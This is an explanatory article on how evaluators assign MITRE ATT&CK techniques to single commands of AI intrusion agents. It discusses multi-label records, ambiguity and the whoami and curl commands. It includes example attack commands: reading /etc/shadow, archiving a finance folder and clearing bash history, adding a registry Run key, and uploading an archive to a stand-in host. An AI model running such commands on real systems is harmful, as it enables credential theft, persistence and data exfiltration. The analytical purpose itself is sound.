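# Assigning ATT&amp;CK techniques to single actions of AI intrusion agents: ambiguity, context and multiple labels

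## ATT&amp;CK labels and the actions of an AI intrusion agent

MITRE ATT&CK (Adversarial Tactics, Techniques, and Common Knowledge) is a public catalogue of how attackers break into computer systems and what they do once inside. The MITRE Corporation, a US non-profit that runs federal research centres, compiles it from real intrusions. Security staff use it mainly as a shared vocabulary. If one firm writes "autorun" and another writes "Run key", both can add the identifier T1547.001 to show that they mean the same technique.

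Researchers who test AI agents on hacking tasks have adopted the ATT&CK vocabulary. These agents are large language models that act through tools. *What Makes a Good LLM Agent for Real-world Penetration Testing?* (2026) describes the standard design, in which the model calls outside functions such as shell commands, and a layer of code around it, the scaffolding, runs the loop of acting and reading the result. Evaluators often run such an agent in a cyber range, a closed network built for practice attacks. Afterwards, the agent's actions are labelled with ATT&CK techniques by a labeller that may be a person, a set of rules or another language model. A single command often fits several techniques, which makes the labelling harder.

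### From tactic to procedure

ATT&CK describes behaviour at four levels. Suppose an attacker on a Linux machine wants other users' passwords. The tactic is the attacker's immediate goal, here Credential Access. The technique is a catalogued way to reach that goal, here OS Credential Dumping (T1003), which covers extracting login secrets from an operating system. The sub-technique is a narrower variant of the technique, here T1003.008, which covers extracting them from /etc/passwd and /etc/shadow, the files where Linux keeps account details and hashed passwords. The procedure is what the attacker actually did, such as running `sudo cat /etc/shadow` to print the second file.

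A labeller works through these levels from the bottom up, because only the procedure leaves a direct trace. *A Graph-Based Approach for Mapping Kernel-Level Telemetry to MITRE ATT&CK* (Lupinacci, Blefari and colleagues, 2026) points out that an action seen in isolation is inherently ambiguous, because one technique can serve several tactics and related techniques often rely on the same low-level operations. Procedures also have no identifiers of their own, so a results table that lists only T1003.008 doesn't show which command received that label. For this reason, MITRE's course for analysts, *Introducing MITRE ATT&CK® for Cyber Threat Intelligence Training* (Pennington, 2024), recommends printing each technique next to its procedure so that other analysts can check the mapping.

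MITRE revises the catalogue regularly. The current version, v20, came out on 13 October 2026, according to MITRE's *Updates* (2026) for that month. The table gives the size of Enterprise, the part of ATT&CK that covers ordinary company networks, in v20 and two earlier versions. Mobile devices and industrial control systems have separate parts. The figures for the earlier versions come from MITRE's *Updates* (2026) for April and *Updates* (2025) for October.

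| Version | Release | Tactics | Techniques | Sub-techniques |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| v18 | October 2025 | 14 | 216 | 475 |
| v19 | 28 April 2026 | 15 | 222 | 475 |
| v20 | 13 October 2026 | 15 | 227 | 479 |

In v19, MITRE split the Defense Evasion tactic into Stealth and Defense Impairment, which raised the number of tactics from fourteen to fifteen. The other thirteen are Reconnaissance, Resource Development, Initial Access, Execution, Persistence, Privilege Escalation, Credential Access, Discovery, Lateral Movement, Collection, Command and Control, Exfiltration and Impact.

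The split complicates comparisons between versions. In *Mapping AI-enabled cyber threats*, Guru, Moix and Klein (2026) studied 832 accounts that the AI company Anthropic had banned for malicious cyber activity, and mapped the account holders' actions to ATT&CK v18. Defense Evasion was the most common tactic, used by 84.4% of the actors. Enterprise ATT&CK no longer has a tactic of that name, so a researcher repeating the count under v20 has to reclassify the cases. Technique labels should therefore include the ATT&CK version number.

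### What an agent's record contains

The basic unit of an agent's record is the action, which is one command or tool call and its output. A useful record also gives the time of each action and the task the evaluators set, and it often includes the reasoning the model wrote before acting. An episode is the complete record of one attempt.

All of these parts can affect the label. Suppose an agent told to reach a database server runs `sudo cat /etc/shadow` on the machine where it starts. The output shows whether the system printed the scrambled passwords or refused. The task shows that the passwords were a means to something else, and the written reasoning may include a plan to try them on the next machine. The command alone shows none of this. The reasoning is evidence of purpose but not proof, because the same model wrote it and the command that follows may do something different.

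*RangeFactory* (2026), a project that builds cyber ranges automatically, records the task context, the exchange between agent and tools, the execution budget and the provenance of each attempt. The provenance covers the range, the collecting agent, how much information the agent received and whether it followed a guide. An autonomous attempt could run for up to 300 turns or one hour. The developers discarded 199 of 5,740 raw records: 73 interrupted by a technical failure, 48 with an incomplete exchange and 78 duplicates. Removing incomplete records also matters for labelling, because a labeller can mistake a gap in the record for a technique that the agent never used.

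Most labelling methods were developed on material other than agent actions. Much of the automated work uses threat reports, which security firms and agencies write after an intrusion. These reports already contain some interpretation. Pennington points out in a course that the report's author has often proposed an intent, while technical detail may have been lost. Reports also come late. Lupinacci and colleagues give the example of SolarWinds, a supply-chain compromise that was discovered in December 2020 and involved more than 70 techniques. Analysts produced the mapping only months after the first break-in, by comparing several companies' reports by hand. A method that recognises techniques from such human descriptions may still fail to recognise them from a bare command.

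System logs are closer to an agent's record, but only partly similar. Lupinacci and colleagues built Trace2ATT&CK, a tool that labels events from the Linux kernel, the core of the operating system. Their cleaned log entries have seven fields: the time, the user, the process, its parent process, the system call, the process name and the arguments. They don't include command output, the task or any reasoning. The logs are also much larger than an agent's record. Running 347 small attack tests produced almost 22 million log lines, or more than 62,000 per test, and the one command that launched a test triggered 24 further program executions on average.

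When an agent downloads a script and runs it in a single line, the agent's record contains one action and the script's printed output, while the kernel log contains every program the script started. An evaluator who labels only the agent's commands can therefore miss techniques carried out inside the script. Labeling only the kernel log would include those programs, but the evaluator would have to infer their purpose.

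Agent records also contain a different kind of noise from server logs. A server's log mixes the intruder's actions with those of ordinary users and background services, so the analyst must first find the attack. An agent's record contains only the agent's actions, but many of them are housekeeping, such as reading a help page or fixing a typing error. Pennington's warning that not every behaviour is a technique applies to these actions too.

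### One label or several

In single-label classification, the labeller gives each item exactly one class from a fixed list. For example, if the labeller assigns T1003.008 to `sudo cat /etc/shadow`, that command cannot have a second label.

In multi-label classification, the labeller may give an item any number of classes, including none. The same command can then have both T1003.008 and T1059 (Command and Scripting Interpreter) as labels, because the attacker read the file through a command shell.

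Trace2ATT&CK uses a single-label evaluation. Its test material comes from Atomic Red Team, an open library of small attack tests. Each test can contain from two to thirty actions but has only one reference label, the technique it was written to imitate. The tool returns a ranked list of candidate techniques for each test, but only one can be correct, so the list reflects uncertainty about a single label rather than an assignment of several.

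MITRE's training assigns multiple labels to single actions. In one exercise, an intruder types eleven Windows commands to look around a machine, and the model answer labels each command with both a Discovery technique and T1059. *CyberClear* (2026), a benchmark for reconstructing attack chains, also allows several techniques per item. It groups 450 annotated instances by their exact set of techniques, which gives 89 distinct behaviours, 46 with one technique and 43 with more than one. A single-label scheme could not fully label nearly half of these behaviours, though the counts do not show what share of the 450 instances needed several labels.

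A multi-label record should list only techniques that are present in the action. If only one of two techniques can be right and the evidence does not settle which, listing both wrongly records that the agent used both.

### Why evaluators label agent actions

The simplest reason to label an agent's actions with ATT&CK techniques is to describe what it did. An episode may contain hundreds of commands, and a list of techniques condenses them into a summary that a reader can understand and a defender can act on. Labels also make patterns visible across many cases. For instance, Guru and colleagues could report that only 54 of their 832 actors used a model for Lateral Movement, the tactic of moving between machines.

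Evaluators also want to compare agents with each other or with human attackers. In *Synthetic APTs*, Balassone, Mayoral-Vilches and colleagues (2026) ran 20 experiments in which agents, all driven by Claude Opus 4.6, imitated five state-linked hacking groups against AI defenders. They measured precision, the share of observed techniques that also appear in the profile ATT&CK publishes for the group. In the ten experiments on an enterprise network, all of which ended in compromise, precision was between 55% and 80%.

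The authors take this as a sign that an agent could pass for the real group. However, their agents' instructions were built from the same ATT&CK pages that were later used to judge the match, so some of the match is expected from an agent that follows its prompt. The precision also depends on the labelling. If a command fits two techniques and only one of them is in the group's profile, the choice of label raises or lowers the precision.

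A third use is measuring coverage, or how much of the catalogue an agent has exercised. *From Capabilities to Performance* (2025), an evaluation of penetration-testing agents, drew its subtasks from ATT&CK tactics to secure both breadth and depth. Readers can convert a technique count into a share of the catalogue only if they know what was counted. For example, Guru and colleagues report 482 unique techniques from 13,873 observations, although Enterprise v18 had only 216 techniques. Their number must include sub-techniques, and their data also contain some entries from the mobile part of ATT&CK. Such counts also depend on how much of the record the labeller treats as one unit.

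In the same data, the number of techniques an actor used correlated only weakly (r = 0.27) with Anthropic's own risk score. The actor with the highest score, a group that ran an espionage campaign through Claude Code with little human help, used 30 techniques across 13 tactics, about as many as dozens of medium-risk actors. Guru and colleagues attribute its higher score to how its software chained the techniques together, for which ATT&CK had no identifier at the time. MITRE has since added AI-focused and AI-enabled techniques in v20. Even so, a list of techniques records which methods an agent used but gives much less information about how well it combined them.

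### The order of work in the CISA guide

The standard instructions for assigning techniques are in *Best Practices for MITRE ATT&CK Mapping*, which the US Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA, 2023) updated in January 2023 with a government research centre that MITRE operates. Analysts following the guide find the behaviour, research it, decide which tactic it serves, and only then look for the technique. Finally, they compare their results with those of other analysts. Pennington's course teaches the same steps in the same order.

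The tactic comes before the technique because it shortens the search. An analyst who has settled on Credential Access does not need to read through all 227 techniques. This order also guards against habit because, according to the course, analysts who go straight to the technique tend to pick one they already know.

A worked example from the course shows how much each step requires. The raw evidence is a command in which a program named recycler.exe processes a file named Shockwave_network.vsdx.

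1. The behaviour is the command itself, which a monitoring tool captured on a Windows machine.
2. Research on the program file reveals that recycler.exe is really RAR, a compression tool, and that the options in the command compress and encrypt. The file ending belongs to Visio, a program for drawing diagrams, so the attacker was probably packing up a network plan.
3. For the tactic, the course proposes Exfiltration, the removal of data from the network, with moderate confidence, and remarks that the commands around this one could make it clearer.
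4. The technique is Archive Collected Data, T1560, and T1059 applies as well.

ATT&CK files T1560 under Collection, not Exfiltration, so the course's tentative tactic and final technique point to different goals, even though its makers chose the example for teaching. What happened next determines whether the attacker was still gathering files or already exfiltrating them.

Both the guide and the course assume an analyst who can examine the program file, question the staff who responded to the incident and read the commands before and after. A labeller who receives one action from an agent's record has only the command and its output. In this example, those would be an unfamiliar program name, some options, a file name and perhaps a line of text from RAR. The agent's full record contains the neighbouring commands in order, and the evaluator decides how many of them the labeller sees.

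## Why one action can fit several techniques

In the recycler.exe example, the attacker's next commands could have shown which tactic applied, but the second label, T1059, would have remained because the attacker used a command shell in either case. Seeing more of the episode resolves some overlaps between techniques but not others, depending on what causes the overlap.

### Six causes of overlap

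The mildest cause is that one technique can serve several tactics. *MITRE ATT&CK* (Strom, Applebaum and colleagues, 2018), the catalogue's design paper, describes tactics as tags that MITRE attaches to a technique according to what an attacker can achieve with it. In the paper's 2020 revision, Process Injection, which means running code inside another program's live process, is tagged as Privilege Escalation because the code can gain the other program's rights, and as Defense Evasion because the code can hide there. If an agent injects code into a service that runs as administrator, the technique is certain but the tactic is not.

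A labeller who chooses the tactic first, as CISA recommends, can miss a technique that isn't tagged with that tactic. In 2020, the sub-technique Process Hollowing was tagged only with Defense Evasion, although its parent, Process Injection, was also tagged with Privilege Escalation. A labeller who had already chosen Privilege Escalation would not have found Process Hollowing under it. MITRE has since split Defense Evasion, so labellers should check the tags in the version of ATT&CK they use.

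A second cause is that some techniques describe the means and others the purpose. Strom and colleagues write that a technique usually describes how an attacker reaches a goal but can also describe what the attacker gains, especially under Discovery. If an agent runs a short Python script that lists the running processes, both Command and Scripting Interpreter (T1059) and Process Discovery (T1057) apply, the first to the means and the second to what the agent learned. This matters more for agents than for most attackers, because an agent with a shell tool sends almost everything through a command interpreter. T1059 will appear on nearly every action if labellers always add it, but rarely if they reserve it for scripts, so evaluators should state which rule they followed.

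Other techniques differ only in goal or direction. Strom and colleagues give the example of an attacker who deletes files. This is File Deletion if the attacker wants to avoid detection, and Data Destruction, under the Impact tactic, if the attacker wants to do damage. The `rm` command can be identical in both cases. The file path sometimes helps to tell them apart, since an agent that deletes its own tools is probably cleaning up, but deleting a folder of server logs could serve either goal.

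The direction of a transfer is usually easier to determine. The command `rclone copy` copies files between a computer and cloud storage, with the source listed first and the destination second. Copying a program from the attacker's storage onto the victim's machine is Ingress Tool Transfer (T1105), and copying the victim's files the other way is Exfiltration to Cloud Storage (T1567.002). The labeller has to check the order of the arguments and know which machine the agent was on and who owned the storage.

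MITRE can have good reasons to separate two techniques that look the same in an agent's record, because it considers more than the actions themselves. Strom and colleagues list six criteria for separating techniques: the objective, the actions, who uses the technique, what it requires, how defenders detect it and how they mitigate it. Only the actions and some of the requirements are likely to show in a command.

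A fourth cause is simply that one line can contain several commands, as in this example:

`ps aux; tar -czf /tmp/f.tgz /srv/finance && rm ~/.bash_history`

In a single command line, the agent lists the running processes (Process Discovery), archives a folder with `tar` (Archive Collected Data) and deletes its command history (Clear Command History). A semicolon separates the first two commands, so the second runs whether or not the first succeeds. The second and third are joined by `&&`, so the third runs only if `tar` succeeds. If `tar` fails, the history is not deleted and the third technique does not apply, so the labeller has to check the output as well as the command line. If the agent had sent the commands separately, the record would contain three actions with one label each, leaving aside T1059 (Command and Scripting Interpreter).

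Parent techniques and sub-techniques also overlap, because any action that fits a sub-technique fits its parent. For example, an agent might run an unfamiliar program that prints password hashes. This output suggests OS Credential Dumping (T1003), but the record may not show whether the program took the hashes from memory or from a file, and those methods fall under different sub-techniques. Strom and colleagues tell analysts to use the parent in such cases and never to map the same procedure to both levels.

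A parent label can also mean that none of the sub-techniques fits. Decider, a tool from CISA (2023), asks an analyst questions about the attacker's behaviour until it reaches a sub-technique, or a technique if no sub-technique fits. If a results table lists only T1003 and the labeller added no note, a reader can't tell whether the labeller lacked the evidence to choose a sub-technique or found a method that the catalogue doesn't list separately.

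The last cause is ATT&CK's definitions. Meng, Jiang and colleagues (2026) argue in *Modeling Semantic Ambiguity* that these describe each technique but often lack guidance on distinguishing it from similar ones. Their example is the sentence "The adversary acquired administrative credentials from the server." One expert might read this as extraction from memory and choose T1003, while another might think of passwords left in an insecure place and choose Unsecured Credentials (T1552).

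More evidence would settle some cases, but not all. Suppose an agent opens the plain-text file in which a file-transfer program keeps its saved logins. Software stores passwords there, which suggests Credentials from Password Stores (T1555), but the file is also unprotected, which suggests Unsecured Credentials (T1552). The labeller already knows everything relevant about the action but lacks a rule, for example that a file counts as a password store if a program created it to keep logins. Without such a rule, two careful labellers can disagree even though neither has overlooked anything.

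### Four situations and how to record them

These causes lead to four situations that people often describe with the same word, "ambiguous". Each calls for a different record.

| Situation | Example | Correct record |
|---|---|---|
| Co-occurring techniques | A Python script lists the running processes | Both techniques: T1059 and T1057 |
| Undetermined technique | An agent deletes a folder of server logs and the goal is unclear | One technique, with its candidates: File Deletion or Data Destruction |
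| Uncertain level of detail | An unfamiliar program prints password hashes | The parent technique only: T1003 |
| Uncertain intent | Someone on a company network displays a computer's network settings | The technique, T1016, with a separate note that the intent is unknown |

When techniques co-occur, several labels clearly apply to the same action. MITRE's *Frequently Asked Questions* describes an attacker who uses PowerShell, a Windows scripting tool, to inject code into lsass.exe and collect passwords from its memory. That procedure contains three techniques or sub-techniques: PowerShell, Process Injection and LSASS Memory. Strom and colleagues also assign two labels to command-and-control traffic that uses HTTP on port 8088, one for the protocol and one for the unusual port.

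Each of these labels needs its own evidence. Strom and colleagues warn that if a report mentions only HTTP traffic, the analyst should not assume it used port 80, the standard HTTP port. More generally, they advise analysts to record a technique only if the source states it or the events could not have happened any other way. That is a strict standard for agent records, where a labeller can easily add a technique because it usually accompanies another.

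An undetermined technique is a single label that the labeller can't yet fill in. The record should list the candidates, marked as alternatives, and give the reason the labeller couldn't choose, because a missing fact may turn up later in the episode, whereas overlapping definitions need a rule for choosing between them. If all the candidates share a tactic, the labeller can at least record the tactic. For example, T1003 and T1552 both belong to Credential Access, but File Deletion and Data Destruction have no tactic in common.

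A list of three labels can therefore mean two things. For the lsass.exe procedure, it means that the attacker used all three techniques. For the sentence about administrative credentials, a list of T1003, T1552 and T1555 would mean that one of the three is right. If an evaluator stores both lists in the same format, a program that counts labels will count six occurrences of techniques where the evidence supports four. The format needs both an "and" and an "or", sometimes for the same action. If a Python script deletes the folder of server logs, the correct record is T1059 and either File Deletion or Data Destruction.

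Uncertainty about the level of detail is easier to handle because every ATT&CK sub-technique has exactly one parent technique. A labeller who can't decide between two sub-techniques of T1003 can record T1003 and lose only detail.

Uncertain intent is a different problem, since the labeller may know which technique a behaviour matches but not whether it was malicious. Strom and colleagues give the example of ipconfig.exe, the Windows program that displays network settings. Running it falls under System Network Configuration Discovery (T1016), but technicians often do so to repair connections. Strom and colleagues let each organisation decide whether to tag every such event or only those from real incidents. Either policy works if the technique and the judgement about intent are recorded in separate fields, so that nobody later mistakes a technician's routine check for part of an attack.

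### The Ambiguous Techniques project

MITRE's Center for Threat-Informed Defense has built a method for cases of uncertain intent. Feffer, Cunningham and Sundar (2025), in *Ambiguous Techniques*, define an ambiguous technique as one whose observable characteristics are insufficient to determine intent. By intent they mean only whether the activity is malicious or benign. The Center's *Ambiguous Techniques Overview* adds that this judgement requires "a preponderance of certainty", but gives no number. The problem is common because many attackers live off the land, using programs already installed on the victim's computers.

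The project team addresses this ambiguity by adding context, which it divides into three kinds. Peripheral context comes from outside the network, such as intelligence about groups that attack banks, and is most useful for Reconnaissance and other activity before a break-in. Chain-level context is the other techniques used before, during or after the one in question. In records of past attacks, the team found that Exfiltration often came immediately after Archive Collected Data, so an archive followed by an upload is more suspicious than an archive alone.

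Technique-level context concerns the single event, and the team sorts it under four questions:

- Who acted, and with what privileges?
- What did they use, such as command options, registry keys or system calls?
- When did it happen, and how often?
- Where did it happen, meaning which files, systems and network connections?

The Center for Threat-Informed Defense's *Context to Determine Intent* includes a flowchart for choosing among the three kinds. A defender first asks whether the activity came before or after the break-in, then whether the attacker brought the tool along, whether someone used it in a non-standard way and whether the user had legitimate access. The last question is whether the activity left an identifiable change or departed from normal behaviour. The defender can tell the purpose of Mimikatz, a password-stealing program, early in this process, but PowerShell's purpose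 is not clear so soon because it was already on the computer.

Defenders then combine their analytics, the searches that flag suspicious events in logs. The Center for Threat-Informed Defense's *Chaining Analytics* describes two ways to do this. One of these, direct correlation, suits a known campaign or tool whose steps depend on each other. For example, if an attacker needs three particular commands for one task, the system raises an alert only when all three analytics have fired.

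Loose correlation suits cases where defenders know only the general pattern. The system counts how many different analytics have fired on one computer, in any order, and raises an alert at a threshold, such as two out of three. Repeated hits from the same analytic count once. Feffer and colleagues also considered strict ordering but concluded that the benefit often doesn't justify the added resources and complexity. Most of the project's chains link only two techniques, because longer ones can exclude relevant activity.

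In the second phase, *Context to Confidence* (Cunningham and Feffer, 2026) scores the log sources that defenders need on six measures: fidelity, noise, timeliness, robustness against evasion, coverage and the context they add. Cost is a separate, optional measure. The definition of an ambiguous technique stayed the same, so the scores rank logs by how well they help separate malicious from benign activity, not one technique from another.

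### What carries over to a known attacker

In a test intrusion, evaluators already know that the agent is the attacker, which settles the project's main question before labelling starts. The correlation rules also give little direct help in choosing labels, because each analytic is already designed to detect a particular behaviour. A loose correlation can show that three Discovery techniques on one computer probably belong to an attack, but not whether a deleted folder was File Deletion or Data Destruction.

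Chain-level context carries over best, though its purpose changes. Defenders look at neighbouring events to judge whether someone is an attacker, while labellers look at them to find out what the attacker wanted. The idea behind direct correlation helps here. If an agent packs a folder into /tmp/f.tgz and then uploads that file, the upload depends on the archive, so the archive was clearly a step towards Exfiltration. Archives often preceded Exfiltration in past attacks, but this is weaker evidence because it doesn't show that a particular agent sent anything out, and Strom and colleagues' warning against assumed techniques applies here.

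Some technique-level context also applies to AI agents. Command options and file locations often distinguish techniques, and privileges sometimes do. The time of day doesn't help, because an agent works whenever the evaluators start it. The nearest equivalent to peripheral context is the evaluators' task description, which can reveal a purpose that isn't clear from the command.

Using intelligence about a real hacking group is riskier. If a labeller uses the group's ATT&CK profile to choose techniques for ambiguous commands, the labelling itself will make an agent that imitates the group, like those of Balassone and colleagues, match the profile more closely.

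Knowing that the actor is an attacker reduces the ambiguity about intent but doesn't remove it. An agent may display its network settings to map the victim's network, or because its own connection has just failed. The second case resembles the technician using ipconfig.exe, except that the repair benefits the attacker. Evaluators have to decide whether such troubleshooting counts as Discovery. The action immediately before it, such as a failed download, will often show why the agent displayed the settings.

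### The Semantic Ambiguity Modeling Framework

Meng and colleagues' Semantic Ambiguity Modeling Framework (SAMF) labels sentences from threat reports with ATT&CK techniques. To choose between techniques that are easy to confuse, it uses a collection of short entries. Each entry describes the behaviour that the techniques share (the context) and how each technique appears in that context (its distinction).

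One entry has the context "malware creates a startup item for persistence". It separates two techniques:

- T1547 (Boot or Logon Autostart Execution) applies when the malware changes system settings so that it starts automatically, through registry keys or startup folders.
- T1059 applies when the malware uses a script or command interpreter to carry out the persistence mechanism.

The paper applies this to a sentence about BadPatch, malware that added a link to its program file in the startup folder. The sentence matches the shared context because the link makes the program start again later. The label is T1547 because the sentence mentions a startup folder, which the distinction for T1547 names, and doesn't mention a script or an interpreter.

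A language model wrote these entries. For each labelled example sentence, the system found similar sentences and gave them to the model with their labels and the official definitions. The model then described what the sentences had in common and how the techniques differed. The 7,794 entries cover 174 techniques. They average 3.2 techniques and 56 words each, while the official definitions average 177 words.

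To label a new sentence, the system retrieves entries with a similar context and asks the model which technique in each entry fits best. The model uses the results to choose a provisional label. The system then retrieves entries that include this label and whose distinctions resemble the sentence, and the model confirms or corrects its choice. Other labelling systems can use this last step to check their answers. On sentences labelled by experts, it improved every system tested.

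The table compares the reported macro-F1 scores of SAMF and four alternatives on two sets of sentences. F1 ranges from 0 to 1 and combines precision with recall, the share of correct labels that the system found. Macro-F1 is the average F1 over all techniques, so a rare technique counts as much as a common one.

| Method | Procedure examples | Expert-labelled sentences |
|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-32B alone | 0.158 | 0.111 |
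| Qwen3-32B with full ATT&CK definitions | 0.520 | 0.330 |
| GPT-5.2 alone | 0.592 | 0.347 |
| TTPXHunter, trained on procedure examples | 0.883 | 0.313 |
| SAMF, using Qwen3-32B | 0.641 | 0.391 |

The comparison with full definitions is the most informative, because the underlying model is the same. Explicit distinctions raised the score by 0.121 on the procedure examples and by 0.061 on the expert-labelled sentences. The procedure examples come from ATT&CK's own pages and average 13 words. SAMF's entries came from a separate part of the same collection. The expert-labelled sentences come from threat reports, average 39 words and are a harder test. SAMF had the best score on these sentences, but it was still low at 0.391, and only 46.5% of its labels were correct.

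Meng and colleagues replaced every sub-technique with its parent before testing, because many sub-techniques had too few examples for a stable score. The results therefore don't show how well SAMF handles uncertainty about the level of detail. In a preliminary check, a simpler method based on definitions reached 81% macro-F1 on sub-techniques in the procedure examples and 71% in the expert set. They conclude that the main difficulty is choosing the technique.

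They tested SAMF only on sentences from reports and ATT&CK pages, not on commands. Such sentences often state the purpose, as in "for persistence", and a command usually doesn't. Consider an agent that types this into a Windows command prompt:

`reg add HKCU\Software\Microsoft\Windows\CurrentVersion\Run /v upd /d C:\Users\Public\u.exe`

The command changes the registry's Run key so that u.exe starts whenever the user logs in. A labeller has to know what the Run key does before the entry about startup items is useful. Two techniques fit this action: T1547, because the agent changed the Run key, and T1059, because it did so through a command interpreter. SAMF gives each sentence exactly one technique, so it would have to drop one of them. A multi-label record should keep both, because the agent used both in the same action.

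Evaluators could still borrow the format for their own labelling rules. For example, an entry for deleted files would have "the agent deletes files on the victim's machine" as its context. The distinction would be that File Deletion applies when the agent removes traces of its own activity, and Data Destruction when it makes the owner's data unavailable. The labeller would then know which fact to look for, which may be in the task description or a neighbouring action, and would leave the technique undetermined if it isn't there.

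## Three commands with several readings: whoami, curl and an SSH login

Evaluators can write such entries in advance for common commands. The programs `whoami`, `curl` and `ssh` are useful examples because administrators and attackers both run them often, and the label for each depends on a different part of the record.

### whoami

`whoami` prints the name of the account that runs it. The obvious label is T1033, *System Owner/User Discovery*, which MITRE defines as an attempt to identify a system's primary user, its current user or the people who commonly use it, or to find out whether someone is using it now. The command also has three other readings.

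| Reading | Technique | Deciding observation |
|---|---|---|
| The agent finds out which account it controls | T1033 | Nothing earlier in the episode had revealed the account |
| The agent looks up groups or privileges | T1069 | The options request them, or the output contains them |
| The agent checks that a login or privilege gain worked | None, or T1033 under a broad rule | The agent already knew which name to expect |
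| The agent looks around its own attack machine | None | The command ran on a machine that belongs to the attacker |

Whether `whoami` has a second reading depends on its options. On Windows, `whoami /groups` lists the account's groups and `whoami /priv` lists its privileges. Both fit T1069, which covers group and permission settings according to MITRE's *Permission Groups Discovery* (2017). The technique isn't limited to group names, since one of MITRE's examples is ShimRatReporter, a tool that gathered the local privileges on an infected machine. On Linux, `whoami` has no such options, so an agent would use `id`, which prints the account name and its groups and therefore supports both T1033 and T1069.

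A detection rule's tags are a poor substitute for reading a command's options. The rule in Elastic's *System Owner/User Discovery Linux* carries both technique tags and fires whenever a program named `whoami`, `w`, `who`, `users`, `id` or `groups` starts. Both tags suit the rule because they cover everything it might catch, but a labeller who copied them onto a plain `whoami` would credit the agent with group discovery when it had seen only a user name.

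The same rule can also miss user discovery. The Center for Threat-Informed Defense's *T1033 System Owner/User Discovery Mappings* lists environment variables such as `$USER` as a way to get this information. An agent that prints the variable with the shell's built-in `echo` command starts no new program, so a rule based on program names doesn't fire. The agent's record still contains the command as typed.

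The output alone isn't a reliable basis for a label either. According to MITRE's definition of T1033, usernames appear throughout a system, for example as the owners of files and processes. `ls -l` prints the owner of each file it lists, so if any username in the output were enough for T1033, most detailed directory listings would count as user discovery.

The check is the hardest reading to separate from discovery. The EQL Analytics Library's *System Owner and User Discovery* (2019), a search rule for Windows events, notes that an attacker may use such commands to learn a privilege level or see whether a session is active. It assigns T1033 in either case. Applying the label this broadly is easy and fits the wording of the definition, since the agent does identify the current user.

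The drawback of the broad rule is that it gives a careful agent extra labels. Suppose two agents each become root, the Linux administrator, on five machines, and only one runs `whoami` on each to make sure. That agent gets five more occurrences of T1033, although it learned nothing about the victim's users that the other agent didn't know.

A narrower rule is to apply T1033 only when the agent could not already predict the account name. After logging in as `alice`, the agent expects `whoami` to return `alice`, so the command only confirms that the login worked. But an agent that has broken into a web server may not know which account the server runs under. T1033 then applies because `whoami` reveals the account, even though the output also confirms the break-in.

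A check that is assigned no technique still belongs in the record because it is evidence about the previous action. For example, if `whoami` prints `alice` after an attempt to become root, the attempt probably failed.

The last reading depends on where the command ran. Many test agents start on their own attack machine, but Discovery techniques concern the victim's systems. Gwak, Strier and colleagues applied a similar rule in *LADE*, a system that uses language models to find and label attack commands. They left all commands meant for the attacker's machines out of their dataset.

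### Whether every shell command needs T1059

Read literally, the definition of T1059 (Command and Scripting Interpreter) covers `whoami` and anything else an agent types into a shell on a victim's machine. MITRE's training follows this reading for its eleven Windows commands. An evaluator who also follows it can compare an agent with intrusions that analysts labelled that way.

For AI agents, though, the T1059 label often describes the test set-up, because evaluators usually decide whether an agent works through a shell. If one agent had a shell and another had a ready-made function that returns the current username, only the first would get T1059, although both looked up the username.

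Where the command runs also matters. When an agent runs `curl` on its attack machine to request a page from the victim's website, it uses the attacker's own shell, so the request alone does not show that an interpreter ran on the victim's machine.

Some detection rules omit T1059 even where it would be informative. Splunk's *Detection* rule for scripts that `curl` downloads and Bash then runs is tagged T1105 (Ingress Tool Transfer) but not T1059. An agent that runs such a script is using an interpreter to execute a whole program, not just a one-word command.

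A workable compromise is to record shell access once for each victim machine and add T1059 to a single action only when the agent uses an interpreter to run a script or inline code. A plain `whoami` would then have only T1033, while a Python script that lists processes would keep both its labels. Evaluators who need the broader labelling for a comparison can add T1059 to the remaining shell commands automatically if the record shows where each one ran.

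### curl

`curl` transfers data to or from a web address. Its possible readings include stealing files, looking at a page, and command and control, which is the traffic an attacker uses to direct a compromised machine.

| Reading | Technique | Deciding observation | Where to find it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fetching a tool or other file | T1105 | The file moves from outside onto a victim's machine | Arguments, and the machine where `curl` ran |
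| Sending data out through the existing control channel | T1041 | The upload uses the channel that already controls the machine | Arguments and earlier actions |
| Sending data out by another protocol | T1048 | The upload uses a different protocol from that channel | Arguments and earlier actions |
| Sending data to a web service | T1567 | The destination is a legitimate service, such as cloud storage | Arguments, if the service is recognisable |
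| Command-and-control traffic | T1071.001 | The exchange carries instructions or their results | Output and later actions |
| Looking at a website | None, or T1594 | The agent only reads the page | Output and later actions |
| Delivering an exploit to a public service | T1190 | The request abuses a weakness in an internet-facing service | Arguments and output, sometimes later actions |
| Querying a cloud metadata service | T1552.005 | The request goes to the metadata address and seeks credentials | Arguments, with the output as confirmation |

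Three simple commands show how far the arguments go:

- `curl -O https://files.example/a` saves a file.
- `curl -T notes.tgz https://files.example/in/` uploads one.
- `curl https://files.example/status` prints the server's response.

**Fetching a file.** Splunk's *Detection* rule for `curl` on Linux matches options that save a file, such as `-O` and `--output`, and assigns T1105. An agent can save the file without these options by redirecting the output with `>`.

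The options also don't show where the file went. MITRE's definition, which Positive Technologies' *T1105* reproduces, requires a transfer from an external system into a compromised environment. If the agent downloads a hacking tool to its own attack machine, it is acquiring a tool (T1588.002). If the file moves between two of the victim's machines, the technique is Lateral Tool Transfer (T1570).

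**Sending a file.** An upload can be theft, but an agent on its attack machine can also use `-T` to push a tool onto a victim's server, which is T1105 even though `curl` is sending the file. The description of T1105 that the Center for Threat-Informed Defense reproduces from v19.1 also covers an attacker who puts a file into a compromised cloud account, where automatic syncing copies it to the victim's machine. The command would look like an upload to cloud storage, which is the usual sign of T1567.

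Gwak and colleagues say T1105 and T1048 are hard to tell apart in code because both commonly rely on the same network tools. Public datasets can add to the confusion, as when Splunk's *Atomic Red Team* dataset stores a log named "curl_upload" under T1105. If an evaluator used the folder name as the reference label, a labeller who recognised that the file was outgoing would be marked wrong.

Once the labeller knows that the agent took data out, the choice between T1041 (Exfiltration Over C2 Channel) and T1048 (Exfiltration Over Alternative Protocol) depends on how the agent controls the machine. If it does so through a program that contacts files.example over the web, uploading notes.tgz through that same channel is T1041. If it controls the machine over SSH, the upload uses a different protocol and is T1048. The `curl` command can be identical in both cases, and the action that set up the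 control channel may be hundreds of commands earlier.

This choice is harder in test set-ups, where the agent may work through a shell that the evaluators provided. The evaluators have to decide whether this connection counts as the control channel. If it doesn't, neither definition fits exactly, because both refer to an existing control channel. The labeller can then record the Exfiltration tactic without a technique and explain why.

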